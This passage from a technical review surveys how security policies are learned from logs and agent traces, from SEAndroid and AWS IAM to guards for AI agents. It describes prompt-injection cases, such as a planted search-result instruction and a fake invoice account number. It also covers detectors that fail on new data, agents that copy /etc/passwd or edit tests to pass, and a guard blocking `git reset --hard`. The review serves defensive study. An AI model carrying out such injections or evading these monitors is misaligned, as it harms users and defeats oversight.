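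Both new kinds of attack targeted SEAndroid itself. In one, untrusted programs tried to alter the files that hold the active policy. In the other, ordinary apps tried to switch to a more privileged process type. EASEAndroid found the second because two of its learners classified a pattern as malicious while the distance learner classified it as benign, which revealed that the program was running under a label it should not have had. So the system could recognise attacks absent from its 17 starting examples, but it relied on the attacks' links to known programs, rules or events. Most of the undecided patterns were too rare to provide such links, and Wang thought some were probably isolated attacks.

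Of the 331 new rules, 51 were allow rules and 280 were `neverallow` rules. The later human-written policy also permitted every access pattern that the 51 allow rules covered. Only 52 of the 280 `neverallow` rules appeared in that policy, and the rest needed further investigation.

EASEAndroid could also create narrower labels. Nine of the benign patterns involved programs reading time-zone files in `/data/misc/zoneinfo`, which carried the default type for everything under `/data`. A rule from audit2allow would have let those programs read every file of that type. EASEAndroid detected that the files shared a folder, proposed a new type for them and wrote a rule for that type alone.

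Wang acknowledges that attackers could mislead the co-occurrence learner by triggering benign actions just before an attack. A log of denials also omits harmful access that the policy already permits, so analysts cannot use it to find existing rules that are too broad.

### Finding rules that are too broad

One way to find such rules is to record the accesses a system's functions need and look for permissions that go beyond them. Wang did this with a second system, SPOKE, which ran 665 functional tests of software for managing company phones and recorded the accesses they made. The tests at least partly justified 1,036 of the 1,356 related policy rules, leaving 320 unjustified. SPOKE found 210 overly permissive accesses among those the 320 rules allowed, and the policy's engineers confirmed the findings and revised the policy. Because the traces come from tests rather than ordinary use, a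 rule may look unjustified only because nobody wrote a test for the function that needs it.

*SEPAL* (Yu, Yang and colleagues, 2021) looked for the same problem across the Android market. Google publishes a base policy, and phone makers add rules for their own hardware and apps. SEPAL learns from the base policy which kinds of access Google allows and forbids, then flags any added rule that resembles the forbidden ones. In 774 system images from 72 manufacturers, it flagged 7,111 of 595,236 added rules as risky or unnecessary.

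Those 7,111 rules were only about 1% of the total, but many were very broad. Yu and colleagues therefore also split the rules into single permissions and calculated what share of the added permissions SEPAL flagged in each version of Android:

| Android version | Flagged share of added permissions |
|---|---|
| 5 | 5.1% |
| 6 | 12.9% |
| 7 | 7.8% |
| 8 | 10.3% |
| 9 | 19.7% |

The share fell in Android 7, after research pointed out some overly broad labels. Yu and colleagues suggest that it rose again because Android 8 separated hardware-specific code from the rest of the system, which left manufacturers with more rules to maintain.

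SEPAL was right about 98.5% of the official rules held back for testing, but less reliable on rules that manufacturers had added. Yu and colleagues checked 368 flagged permissions on one Huawei phone by hand and confirmed that 283 (77%) were unnecessary and too permissive. Another 40 were false alarms, and they couldn't settle most of the rest without more documentation.

One flagged rule let every process on the phone read certain links belonging to every other process. Yu and colleagues say this could happen when someone simply accepts the output of audit2allow. They did not establish how often it does, and the explanation does not quite fit this rule, which used a group name covering all processes. In Red Hat's example, audit2allow names the specific types in the log. Other flagged rules were left over from testing or from older versions of Android.

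On one ASUS phone, such a rule let untrusted apps find the service that controls the screen lock. Yu and colleagues added the rule to an emulated phone and exploited a separate vulnerability to get past the service's own check. An app could then reset the password.

They reported problems to seven manufacturers. Four confirmed the findings but removed only some of the rules. The manufacturers explained that removing a rule might break something, and that sometimes even their developers did not know why a rule was there. Adding an exception when a program fails is much easier than proving years later that nothing depends on it.

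### Recommending rules from similar programs

The methods described so far write allow rules only for accesses that appear in a log. CASPR, built by Xiao and colleagues, also suggests permissions that a program has not yet requested, based on what similar programs are allowed to do. It clusters process types by their existing permissions, the locations of their files, how close together their actions appear in the logs, and the groups they already belong to. If most members of a cluster have a permission and one lacks it, the missing permission becomes a candidate. CASPR clusters object types in the same way and recommends a rule only when both clusterings support it.

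For example, CASPR recommended letting the service that manages virtual machines read a directory used for messages between programs. The services that manage the computer's name, clock and language settings could already read it.

Xiao and colleagues trained CASPR on 90% of the rules in each of six Linux policies and tested whether it could recover the rest. Its average accuracy was 91.6%, and its false positive rate was 13.7%, meaning it recommended about one in seven of the tested accesses that the policy did not allow. For newly created types, which have no rules yet, accuracy was 82.4%. Xiao and colleagues set a stricter threshold for these types because they considered excessive permissions worse than missing ones.

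These figures measure agreement with the existing policy. If that policy is too broad, reproducing its mistakes raises CASPR's score. Similar programs do not need identical permissions, and Xiao and colleagues warn against adding the recommended rules blindly.

A language model could also read the log and write the rules itself. *Generation of Human Comprehensible Access Control Policies from Audit Logs* (2026) tried this for human users and found that performance began to degrade above about 700 log entries, even after the log was compressed. It worked better to have an ordinary algorithm derive the rules, while the model wrote code to parse the log and then explained the finished rules in plain language.

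### Cloud permissions from activity logs

Cloud providers also derive policies from logs. In Amazon Web Services (AWS), programs act through roles, and policies determine what each role may do. The CloudTrail service logs the roles' activity, and IAM Access Analyzer can draft a policy from the log. An administrator picks a role and a period of up to 90 days, then reviews and completes the draft. Administrators usually do this to replace a broad policy with a narrower one, whereas audit2allow adds permissions to a policy that has blocked something.

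AWS's *IAM Access Analyzer policy generation* sets out what the draft covers:

| Part of the policy | What the draft contains |
|---|---|
| Actions in some services, such as EC2 virtual servers | The actions found in the log |
| Actions in other services | The name of the service, with the actions left for the administrator to add |
| Data events, such as those in S3 file storage | No individual actions |
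| `iam:PassRole`, permission to hand a role to a service | Nothing, because CloudTrail does not track it |
| Resources, such as a particular storage area | A placeholder, or a star for all resources if the action cannot be restricted further |

In an example on the AWS security blog, a fictional developer, Sofía, has to complete the draft policy herself. The draft shows that her application used a message queue, but not what it did there, so she adds permission to send and receive messages because she knows the application needs to do both. She must also replace the placeholders with the resources that the application uses. If she used a wildcard (*) there, the application could use every queue in the account.

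Suppose the office agent kept its files in S3. Reading a stored file is a data event, so the draft would not list it, and the administrator would have to decide whether the agent may read, change or delete files, and in which folders. These choices are among the most important for preventing a leak.

AWS recommends choosing the shortest possible log period so that the draft is ready sooner, but even the maximum of 90 days can miss an annual task. The tool also reviews actions that AWS denied, so the administrator should check that the draft does not grant any that were rightly denied.

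Analysing a program's code avoids some of these gaps, since code shows what the program can do even if it has not done it recently. AWS (2025) released a free tool, IAM Policy Autopilot, that drafts policies from application code and works with AI coding assistants such as Claude Code. Since August 2026, it can also read plan files from Terraform, a tool for setting up cloud systems (AWS, *IAM Policy Autopilot now supports Terraform plan files*, 2026). An agent's code shows which cloud services its tools can call, but the model selects which tools to use, and on what, during each run.

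AWS nevertheless recommends log-based policies for agents. *AGENTSEC03-BP03 Implement least privilege with dynamic boundaries* advises companies to use Access Analyzer to derive a baseline from an agent's recorded activity. They should then set a permission boundary, an upper limit that holds even if someone later widens the agent's policy, and review permissions every quarter to remove unused ones. The guidance also lists a common mistake, which is expanding an agent's permissions after access errors without investigating whether the access was legitimate.

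A baseline from 90 days of activity combines everything the agent did, so an office agent that also handled payroll would keep access to the salary files while preparing research summaries. For this reason AWS also recommends issuing temporary credentials for each task, valid for 15 to 60 minutes and limited to the permissions the task requires. Someone still has to decide what those permissions are, and a log of cloud activity does not show which task each action was for.

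## Learning allowlists from the traces of AI agents

A cloud activity log shows which services an agent used. An agent's own trace can also contain the user's request, the model's written reasoning, and the input and result of every tool call. AgentGuardian, whose file-reading rule appeared in the first section, builds an allowlist from these traces. Abaev and colleagues designed the system to control the inputs to each tool and the order of tool calls.

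### How AgentGuardian builds a policy

During staging, people use the agent normally while a logging tool records each run. AgentGuardian then builds the policy in five steps:

1. It extracts the sequence of tool calls from each run.
2. It draws a graph of permitted orders, with an arrow from one tool to another if the second directly followed the first in at least one run.
3. It converts each call into an embedding, a list of 150 numbers chosen so that similar calls get similar lists.
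4. It sorts each tool's embeddings into clusters.
5. For each cluster, it writes a rule consisting of a text pattern for the tool's input and a range for each numeric attribute.

The 150 numbers describe these features:

| Feature | Numbers |
|---|---|
| Length of the model's input and output, earliest and latest hour, idle time, processing time | 6 |
| The model's written reasoning | 32 |
| Type of tool | 16 |
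| Input to the tool | 64 |
| Result of the task | 32 |

AgentGuardian groups similar inputs and drafts text patterns from the beginnings and endings they share. A language model, Claude Sonnet 4.5, then merges these drafts into a shorter set that should still match every legitimate input in the record. AgentGuardian takes the numeric limits from the extreme values in the cluster.

Suppose the agent wants to call tool *T* with text input *x* and numeric attributes *a*, and *T* has *K* clusters. AgentGuardian permits the call if

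path(*T*) ∧ (*R*₁(*x*, *a*) ∨ *R*₂(*x*, *a*) ∨ … ∨ *R*_K(*x*, *a*)),

where ∧ means "and", ∨ means "or", and path(*T*) is true if the graph contains the route by which the agent reached *T*. Each rule has the form

*R*ₖ(*x*, *a*) = [*x* matches pattern *k*] ∧ [minₖ(*u*) ≤ *a*(*u*) ≤ maxₖ(*u*) for every attribute *u*].

A call needs to satisfy only one cluster's rule, so the policy loses some of the distinctions that the clustering found. The clustering takes the model's reasoning into account and might therefore separate payroll work from research summaries, but the finished rules do not check that reasoning. If one cluster's pattern permits `HR/salaries.txt`, the agent may also open that file during a research summary, unless the graph or a numeric limit prevents it. AgentGuardian reduces this problem by writing separate policies for agents with different roles.

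The graph can stop some injected actions by itself. In Abaev and colleagues' example, a research agent lists the files in a folder, reads one or more of them and then searches the web. After a search, it can search again or create a directory, but it cannot go back to reading files. An instruction planted in a search result therefore could not make this agent open another file.

The same graph allows a web search only after a file listing and at least one file read, even though the application treats the local folder as optional. If a user supplied no folder, the agent would presumably need to start with a search, which the graph forbids.

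AgentGuardian checks each call through LiteLLM, a software library that connects agents to language models. If a call violates the policy, AgentGuardian raises an alert and notifies the model, which interrupts the run. In critical cases it can shut the agent down.

### Two applications and 100 test runs

Abaev and colleagues tested AgentGuardian on a knowledge assistant, which writes research summaries and emails them, and an IT support application, which diagnoses computer faults. For each application, they generated 100 benign inputs, using 60 for staging and 40 for testing, and added ten misuse cases. The agents ran on GPT-4.1.

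| Result | Knowledge assistant | IT support | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Misuse cases accepted | 0 of 10 | 2 of 10 | 2 of 20 |
| Benign runs rejected | 5 of 40 | 3 of 40 | 8 of 80 |
| Benign runs that failed because of model errors | 4 of 40 | 2 of 40 | 6 of 80 |

Four of the eight rejected runs broke a numeric limit, even though the test allowed values up to twice the limit. Their inputs were up to five times as long as expected, or their processing times up to ten times as long. The other four used tools in an order missing from the graph, which Abaev and colleagues attribute to too few staging samples. The text patterns caused no false rejections.

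The six model errors are counted separately, as the benign execution failure rate. In these runs the request was legitimate, but the model invented file names or proposed irrelevant tools, and AgentGuardian flagged the resulting calls. It is reasonable not to blame the policy for these failures, but 14 of 80 legitimate requests (17.5%) still did not go through as intended.

When Abaev and colleagues repeated the evaluation with the smaller model GPT-4o mini, these failures rose from 4 to 24 in the knowledge assistant and from 2 to 13 in IT support. They also found that smaller models' planning errors entered the staging traces and produced worse policies, so staging traces can contain bad examples even when no attacker is involved.

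The misuse cases were an easier test than the prompt injections that AgentGuardian is meant to stop. Two misuse examples from the knowledge assistant contain the malformed email addresses `gracewilson@@mail` and `isabellahughes.mailc`, and one of these examples also names the folder `C:\Program Files`. One benign example contains a well-formed Gmail address. A rule that accepts Gmail addresses would probably accept an attacker's Gmail address too, so catching all ten cases is weak evidence that AgentGuardian could prevent a leak by email. The IT support cases were closer to real attacks. In one, someone complained of a slow computer and then asked the agent to list every user on the company network.

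### What the published rule permits

According to its caption, the file-reading rule permits only text files in the `Cars` and `AI` folders, and those in `AI` must have names that start with `ai` and end with `-2025`. But the path pattern ends with a catch-all, so deleting the two alternatives that name these folders would not change which paths it accepts.

| Path | Within the caption's description? | Accepted by the pattern? |
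|---|---|---|
| `./Cars/a.txt` | yes | yes |
| `./AI/ai-chips-2025.txt` | yes | yes |
| `./AI/ai-chips-2024.txt` | no | yes |
| `./HR/salaries.txt` | no | yes |
| `./../private/notes.txt` | no | yes |
| `./Cars/sales report.txt` | yes | no |

The two dots in the fifth path lead to the folder above the agent's working folder, so the pattern would let the agent leave its working folder unless another check stopped it. The sixth path fails only because the file name contains a space.

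One of the benign examples uses a folder called `./Cardiology`, which suggests how the last alternative got into the pattern. If the staging runs included files from this folder or others like it, the merged pattern had to cover them, and the model may have added a catch-all instead of naming more folders.

The rule's time window, 07:33 to 20:25, shows only when the recorded runs took place, because the researchers generated the inputs themselves. The caption describes it as normal working hours. The 9.8-second limit on processing time also depends partly on the speed of the computers and language model used.

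Using recorded extremes as limits also causes false rejections at a predictable rate. If new runs resemble the recorded ones and their order is random, a new value exceeds the largest of *n* recorded values with probability 1/(*n* + 1), or 1.6% for 60 values. But AgentGuardian sets limits separately for each cluster, and in a cluster of five calls the probability is 17%. Abaev and colleagues doubled the permitted value in their test, which makes such rejections rarer, but they did not apply this margin to the time of day.

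### Why ten examples gave a looser policy than 60

When AgentGuardian learned a policy for a file-writing tool, ten staging samples led to a pattern that accepted practically any text, while 60 samples led to a much more restrictive one. We might expect a policy learned from little data to be too tight instead, since the data contains few legitimate actions.

Abaev and colleagues present this as evidence that more samples make a better policy, and the way the method works may explain why. Suppose a small record contains only the paths `./Cars/a.txt` and `minutes.md`. They have no beginning or ending in common, so a single pattern covering both may have to accept any text. Adding `./Cars/b.txt` and `agenda.md` reveals two groups, and the patterns `./Cars/*.txt` and `*.md` cover all four paths.

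New examples can only add to what Systrace and the sequence detectors accept, so if *P* is part of a larger record *P*′, then *g*(*P*) is part of *g*(*P*′). AgentGuardian instead recalculates its clusters and patterns, so *g*(*P*′) can be smaller than *g*(*P*). Whether a small record makes a policy too tight or too loose therefore depends on the generalisation step.

Ordinary use would not reveal the problem, because the text pattern learned from ten samples would pass every benign test. Abaev and colleagues considered testing policies learned from small samples on the remaining inputs, but found this impractical because the patterns accepted everything. The catch-all in the file-reading rule shows that a larger sample does not guarantee a tight pattern either.

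### Learning from users' decisions

AgentGuardian learns what an agent usually does, which may differ from what the user wants. An agent that sends a passport number with every flight booking will produce a consistent record, even if domestic flights do not require one.

Another approach is to learn from people's decisions about permissions. Wu, Yang and colleagues (2025), in *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, asked 205 people to train an imaginary personal assistant by deciding which data it could share in situations involving health, finance, entertainment and other subjects. Their decisions depended on the situation and the type of data, but each person's preferences were fairly consistent and often resembled other people's.

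The prediction system combines two methods to take advantage of this. A language model is given examples of the user's earlier decisions and predicts the next one, while collaborative filtering bases predictions on the choices of people with similar preferences. The language model needs no retraining to handle types of data that nobody has asked about before.

The predictions matched participants' decisions 85.1% of the time. Without a user's history, accuracy was 66.9%, but adding the user's decisions on one to four earlier requests raised it by 10.8%. When the system made only high-confidence predictions, accuracy reached 94.4%. Wu and colleagues report that this stricter threshold affected 74.1% of the data, but they don't make clear whether the system decides those cases or skips them.

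Accuracy here means agreement with what a person chose in an imagined situation. Wu and colleagues found that participants often granted too much or too little access, so a system that predicts their decisions perfectly would repeat those mistakes. The predictions also cover only data sharing, so a prediction that Ana would let her assistant use her calendar data does not show whether the assistant should delete tomorrow's meeting.

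### Teaching an agent what a task requires

The same user may want an agent to open the salary file for one task and leave it alone for the next. Zhou and Zhang describe several systems that derive permissions from the task itself, including MiniScope, which selects permissions to cover the agent's proposed plan. Tu and Tu (2026), in *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents*, instead train the agent to use no more authority than its task requires. (MCP, the Model Context Protocol, is a common standard for connecting agents to tools.)

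They score each action from 0 to 1 on six kinds of authority: changing data, running code, reaching outside the environment, reading secrets, affecting a broad range of things, and leaving lasting changes. For a whole run, **z** contains the highest score on each. Every task *x* also has an envelope **z**_req(*x*), the authority sufficient to complete it. The excess is

Δ = max(**z** − **z**_req(*x*), 0),

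calculated separately for each kind of authority. If the task is to read a bug report and suggest a fix, editing a file counts as excess. If the task is to copy information into a database, writing to that database does not.

Tu and Tu used reinforcement learning to train a small language model, Qwen3.5-4B, on 1,500 tasks. The reward increased when the model completed the task and gathered the necessary evidence, and decreased when it used excess authority, attempted forbidden actions or took unnecessary steps. They then tested the model on outside benchmarks and on 500 new tasks, 200 of them from task families absent from training.

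| Measure | Before training | After training |
|---|---|---|
| Safe success on the 500 tasks | 64.36% | 98.48% |
| Runs with excess authority on the 500 tasks | 4.56% | 0.79% |
| Excessive choices on the FORTIS benchmark | 43.28% | 40.72% |
| Excessive choices on ToolPrivBench | 45.2% | 45.0% |
| The same, with an instruction to use least privilege | 41.2% | 37.9% |

A run is a safe success if it completes the task correctly, with enough evidence and without excess authority. After training, 988 more of the 2,896 runs were safe successes, but only 109 fewer had excess authority. Most of the improvement therefore came from completing tasks correctly and with enough evidence. The table shows the best of three training attempts, which reached 97.63% safe success on a smaller set of tasks, while the others reached about 86%.

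The difference between the first and fourth rows clearly shows that the learning did not transfer. The trained model completed every run safely in the 200 tasks from unfamiliar families, but these tasks used the same kind of environment and checks as the training tasks. ToolPrivBench presents a different choice. *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?* (Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues, 2026) explains that each of its 544 scenarios offers three standard tools and three more powerful ones, any of which could do the job. The first call to each standard tool fails with a temporary error, which gives the agent a reason to use a more powerful one.

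Tu and Tu then trained the model on another 400 tasks, half of them modelled on ToolPrivBench, and the model's rate of excessive choices on that benchmark fell from 45.0% to 38.1%. They take this as evidence that the framework can adapt to new domains. It also suggests that someone must first notice a weakness and write tasks to correct it.

Parkinson and colleagues tested a simpler intervention that required no training. They added a label to each tool's description showing how much privilege the tool carries. Across eight models, this reduced excessive choices by up to 19.3 percentage points, while irrelevant labels in the same format had no such effect. On most models, the labels alone mainly delayed the use of a powerful tool until the agent had tried all the standard ones. Combining the labels with an instruction to use least privilege more often prevented the powerful tool's use.

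Neither method creates a permission policy, because the model can still choose an excessive action. Tu and Tu recommend keeping permission checks and isolated environments around the trained agent. In their method, task designers supply the envelopes, so they must still decide what each task requires.

### Checking whether a trace makes sense

An agent can call its usual tools in the usual order and still do the wrong thing. For example, a clinic assistant might look up a patient's symptoms and then fetch instructions for visiting a department, as it normally does, but send a patient with back pain to psychiatry. In *TraceAegis*, Liu, Ruan and colleagues (2025) built a system that learns both the order of calls and the conditions under which each action is appropriate.

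TraceAegis first uses normal traces to arrange the tools in levels, with tools that can occur in either order on the same level. It then cuts each trace into short units, so a visit to orthopaedics and psychiatry becomes one unit for each department. A language model summarises the conditions for each kind of unit, for example that knee or arm pain leads to orthopaedics. When a new trace arrives, TraceAegis checks that its units have occurred before, and a language model then compares their conditions with the summaries.

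Liu and colleagues tested this on the clinic assistant and a purchasing assistant. For each, they generated 1,300 normal traces and 300 abnormal ones, half with unfamiliar tool sequences and half with familiar sequences in the wrong circumstances. The best configuration for the clinic assistant caught 289 of the 300 abnormal traces, and its reported precision implies about ten false alarms among 300 normal ones. The best configuration for the purchasing assistant caught 280. All 20 traces it missed had familiar tool sequences, so checking the order of the tools could not have caught them.

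Cutting the traces into units was essential. Without this step, one model's F1 score, which combines the share of abnormal traces caught with the share of alarms that are correct, fell from 0.948 to 0.499. In one example, the system merged visits to three departments into a single muddled rule.

The comparison of conditions is permissive. The language model is instructed to accept a set of conditions if at least one resembles an expected condition, even if the set includes others. This avoids rejecting a patient who describes knee pain in new words or mentions an additional symptom, but it could also let through an abnormal request that includes one ordinary condition.

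In another test at a technology company, TraceAegis caught 132 of 140 traces that the company's security testers had altered. Liu and colleagues do not report how many false alarms it raised in that test.

### Tracing where each value came from

In the office agent's leak, the outside address came from a stranger's web page. *Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira and colleagues, 2026) uses this kind of information directly. It records whether each argument came from the user, a trusted tool or an untrusted source such as an email.

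Agent-Sentry checks an action in up to three stages:

1. A classifier examines the sequence of calls and the sources of their arguments, then allows the action, blocks it or passes it on.
2. An allowlist contains sensitive values from earlier benign runs, such as recipients and account numbers. The system allows the action if these values are on the list or if it can confirm that they came from a trusted source.
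3. A language model compares the remaining actions with the user's request.

Suppose a user asks the agent to pay the bill in `bills.txt`, and the file contains an unfamiliar account number. The first two stages cannot determine whether the payment is legitimate, so the language model checks how the number appears in the file. A number in the ordinary text of a bill is acceptable, but one that appears in an instruction to use a different account suggests an attack. Sequeira and colleagues acknowledge that a convincing fake invoice could get past this check.

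Agent-Sentry has the strongest result among these systems on a large test of prompt injection. The test contained 3,299 benign traces and 2,081 successful attacks from seven agents. Agent-Sentry allowed 96.4% of the benign traces and blocked 96.8% of the attacks, using the language model for only 3.1% of its decisions. On two existing benchmarks, AgentDojo and AgentDyn, it blocked 94.3% of attacks and allowed about 95% of benign runs.

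The classifier behind these results learned from traces labelled as attacks as well as from normal behaviour. A second version replaces the classifier with rules about combinations of warning signs. If none of these rules applies, the first stage allows the action, so that stage works more like a denylist.

### Learning errors or learning the test

A detector can also learn mainly from examples of failure. In *TrajAD*, Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) took about 32,000 successful agent traces and made a faulty copy of each, so half of their data contained manufactured errors. To make each copy, they introduced an error at a chosen step, such as a wrong tool, a pointless loop or a failure to stop, and had a language model continue the run from there.

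They trained a small model to recognise the faulty traces and find the first wrong step. It reached an average F1 score of 81.8%, compared with 70.4% before training, but located and described the error correctly in only 53.8% of cases. To test whether it generalised, they trained it on four domains and withheld the fifth, which consisted of tasks in simulated physical environments. It detected errors in the withheld domain almost as well as a model trained on all five, scoring 83.1% compared with 83.8%, but was much worse at locating them.

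This is encouraging evidence that the detector transfers between domains. But the errors in every domain were manufactured by the same process, so the detector may partly have learned to recognise that process. The errors were also mistakes and inefficiencies rather than attacks.

In *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026) tested this concern by training several detectors on AgentDrift, a collection of artificial traces, and evaluating them on AgentDojo. They measured performance by AUROC, the probability that a detector scores a randomly chosen hijacked run higher than a randomly chosen benign one. An AUROC of 0.5 is no better than guessing.

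| Detector | Trained and tested on AgentDrift | Trained on AgentDrift, tested on AgentDojo |
|---|---|---|
| General behaviour, such as the number of calls | 0.830 | 0.482 |
| Behaviour and tool names | 0.879 | 0.473 |
| Order of calls | 0.936 | 0.513 |
| Full text | 0.999 | 0.520 |

The full-text detector did best on the original data because it relied on accidental features of the text. For instance, the token "2026" appeared in 74% of benign training traces but under 5% of hijacked ones. Similarly, five fixed phrases appear in almost all of AgentDojo's hijacked traces and none of its benign ones, so just searching for them gives an AUROC of 0.998.

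New tools were a separate problem for the detector based on the order of calls. Its score fell from 0.936 to 0.674 when Abbasi and colleagues hid the names of all the tools in AgentDrift. Randomly hiding some names during training made the drop smaller, because it exposed the detector to unfamiliar tools.

These experiments show why a high score on one collection is weak evidence, but they used the researchers' own detectors, so TraceAegis, TrajAD and Agent-Sentry would not necessarily fail in the same way. Six of the 11 published evaluations that Abbasi and colleagues reviewed included no test on a second benchmark or data source. Agent-Sentry's main test used different user tasks from those in training, but its designers had paired every user task with the same injection tasks, so the attackers' goals in the test had already appeared in training.

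False alarms can also be much more common on other data. *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic* (2026) mentions a detector trained on 35,000 artificial traces that flagged 66.7% of benign data.

One detector in the study by Abbasi and colleagues, AlignmentCheck, did work on AgentDojo, with an AUROC of 0.930. It prompts a general language model to judge whether each action serves a goal that the user did not set, and it was not trained on either collection. At its standard setting, it flagged 90% of the hijacked runs but also 17.3% of the benign ones. If 2% of an organisation's runs were hijacked, about nine in ten alerts would be false.

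## Turning agent failures into deny rules

After an agent causes harm, a company can write a rule to stop it from doing the same thing again. The same failure can justify a narrow rule or a much broader one, as the office agent's leak showed. Several systems from 2026 make this choice automatically. They write the rule in ordinary language and use a model to apply it to new situations.

### From one incident to one rule

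Incident response is the routine that security teams follow after a breach, and Xiao, Sun and Chen (2026), in *AIR*, apply it to AI agents. AIR starts with descriptions of possible incidents, which people normally write in advance. Each description names a tool, a condition to check after the agent uses that tool, and a repair. AIR then works in four steps:

1. **Detection.** After each tool call, the agent's model inspects the environment and the recent steps to decide whether a described incident has happened.
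2. **Containment.** If it has, the agent stops the harm, for example by deleting a leaked copy of a file.
3. **Recovery.** The agent restores a safe state and abandons the original task.
4. **Eradication.** The model writes a new rule describing the kind of plan that led to the incident. In later runs, AIR compares each plan with this rule and blocks a matching action before the tool runs.

In one example, a user asks a coding agent to tidy a project folder and report on the system's configuration. The agent copies `/etc/passwd`, which lists the computer's user accounts, into a temporary folder. This matches the incident description "a sensitive file has been copied into an unprotected directory". The agent deletes the copy and checks for others. AIR then adds a rule against plans to copy files "from system directories into user-level folders".

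The incident description depends on whether the file is sensitive, whereas the new rule depends on where the file comes from. The two therefore disagree about some actions, as these examples show:

| Planned action | Would it fit the incident description? | Would the new rule block it? |
|---|---|---|
| Copy `/etc/passwd` into `./tmp/` | yes | yes |
| Copy `/etc/timezone` into `./tmp/` | no | yes |
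| Copy `HR/salaries.txt` into `./tmp/` | yes | no |
| Email the contents of `/etc/passwd` | no | no |

The new rule is broader than the incident because it covers harmless system files, such as the one that stores the computer's time zone. Xiao and colleagues point out that the agent can still copy ordinary project files, but a report on the system's configuration may need some of those system files too. The rule is also narrower than the incident because it misses sensitive files stored elsewhere, such as the salary file. Both points assume that the rule is read literally. A model might interpret it more broadly and protect the salary file, but the model's decisions would be harder to predict than those of a fixed pattern.

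Fixed patterns can also be too broad and too narrow at once. *Lessons Outlive Their Failures* (Hassanzadeh Aliabadi, 2026) describes a guard that searched an agent's commands for forbidden text. It blocked a harmless documentation edit that quoted a forbidden command. It also missed variants of `git reset --hard`, which can destroy unsaved work, just as the `git push` rule in the first section missed variants of its command.

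### How well AIR prevented repeats

Xiao and colleagues tested AIR on coding agents, web-browsing agents and agents in a simulated household, all running on GPT-5. They gave the agents risky tasks and counted only the tasks that led to an incident. An incident counted as eradicated if AIR wrote a rule that prevented it in future runs.

| Agent | Incidents | Detected | Eradicated |
|---|---|---|---|
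| Coding | 567 | 542 (95.6%) | 535 (94.4%) |
| Household | 143 | 143 (100%) | 138 (96.5%) |
| Browser | 47 | 44 (93.6%) | 43 (91.5%) |

The coding tasks covered 25 categories of risk, and AIR detected every incident in 20 of them, including deleting sensitive files and giving an outsider remote control of the computer. All 25 missed incidents came from the other five categories, which involved flaws in code the agent wrote. For instance, AIR detected 22 of 30 cases of biased code and eradicated 17. Xiao and colleagues attribute some of the low figures to the agent not producing the intended flaw. A subtle flaw in a program may also be harder to recognise than a deleted file.

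These rates are for familiar kinds of harm, because Xiao and colleagues wrote the incident descriptions from the risk categories in each dataset. AIR learns a deny rule only after it detects an incident, so it learns no rules for harm that nobody has described.

They also repeated a random sample of tasks over three rounds, keeping the rules from earlier rounds and letting AIR add or refine them:

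| Agent | Tasks | Incidents in round 1 | Round 2 | Round 3 | Final number of rules |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Coding | 100 | 54 | 6 | 0 | 9 |
| Household | 100 | 67 | 5 | 2 | 11 |
| Browser | 50 | 8 | 1 | 0 | 6 |

Nine rules stopped 54 incidents, so some rules must have covered several tasks. But the later rounds used the same tasks that had produced the rules. The results show that AIR can prevent repeats, but give little evidence about tasks outside the sample.

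The test also does not show how much legitimate work the new rules would block. Xiao and colleagues ran 85 safe tasks, some deliberately similar to risky ones, such as microwaving a potato instead of a fork, and AIR flagged none of them as incidents. But this tested the incident descriptions, and they do not report a similar test of the deny rules. Running the checks made safe tasks take 40% to 44% longer.

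Xiao and colleagues found that one incident description could usually cover a group of similar tasks, but a different kind of risk needed a separate description. Each coding category needed only one description, while household categories needed two to five and browser categories needed three or four.

GPT-5 could also write the descriptions after seeing three examples by developers and some of the risky tasks. With its descriptions, detection rates were 84.6% for coding agents, 96.0% for household agents and 88.6% for browser agents. Some descriptions were too narrow, such as one about putting a metal fork in a microwave, which could miss other dangerous objects. Others were too abstract, such as a warning that a microwave may cause a fire, which could flag harmless cooking. Xiao and colleagues recommend that people check and correct what the model writes.

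### Merging hundreds of failures into 15 rules

AIR writes rules one incident at a time, whereas *AgentGuard* (Dai and Wang, 2026) derives rules from 642 recorded failures by coding agents and then merges the rules. Reviewers had already marked the action that went wrong in each failure. (AgentGuard is unrelated to AgentGuardian, which learns allowlists.)

AgentGuard summarises each failure as a finding, which consists of the context, the action, its outcome, the supporting evidence and the stage of the work. It then converts the finding into a rule with five fields. Suppose a user asks an agent to fix a bug without changing the tests. A test expects a function to return 10, but the function returns 12. The agent edits the test to expect 12, so the test passes and the bug remains. AgentGuard would produce a rule like this:

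| Field | Content | Where it comes from |
|---|---|---|
| When | The task calls for a fix to the source code, and a test reveals the bug | Context |
| DoNot | Change the test to get past the failure | Action |
| Unless | The task explicitly asks for a correction to the test | Conditions under which the task would permit the action |
| Instead | Fix the code and run the test again | Smallest change that avoids the bad outcome |
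| ApplyAt | Changing and checking the project | Stage |

The Unless field matters because tests sometimes contain mistakes, and fixing them is legitimate work. In the notation of the first section, the field removes some actions from *N* ∩ *g*(*F*), the false rejections of a denylist. But a trace of an agent weakening a test does not show when changing a test would be right, so the exceptions have to be based on other information.

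AgentGuard also replaces details such as file paths and error messages with general terms, provided that this does not change when the rule applies. It then merges the rules using three operations:

- **Removing duplicates.** If two rules forbid the same action at the same stage, under compatible conditions and with the same alternative, AgentGuard keeps one and combines their evidence.
- **Absorbing specific rules.** A general rule can replace a specific one if it covers the same cases without restricting any more legitimate work. It must keep the specific rule's exceptions.
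- **Resolving conflicts.** If two rules call for different responses to what looks like the same action, AgentGuard keeps them separate or makes their conditions more precise.

It repeats these operations until the rules stop changing. Finally, it discards any rule that lacks evidence from a trace, depends on something the agent cannot observe before acting, offers no clear alternative, or interferes with legitimate work.

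Dai and Wang derived 15 rules from 461 failures across 282 tasks and kept another 100 tasks for testing. When summarized, many of the rules resemble general advice for programmers, such as diagnosing a failed command before retrying it or avoiding unrelated changes when editing code. The full versions are more specific and include exceptions. Before each instruction, the agent loads only the rules relevant to that type of work.

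### Fewer failures, more refusals

Each of the 100 test tasks combined several legitimate steps with one intended to cause trouble, such as an unsafe request, a missing file or an ambiguous instruction. Dai and Wang ran every task three times with the rules and three times without, using Claude Code with Claude Haiku 4.5.

| Outcome | Without rules (300 runs) | With rules (300 runs) |
|---|---|---|
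| Abnormal behaviour | 207 (69.0%) | 80 (26.7%) |
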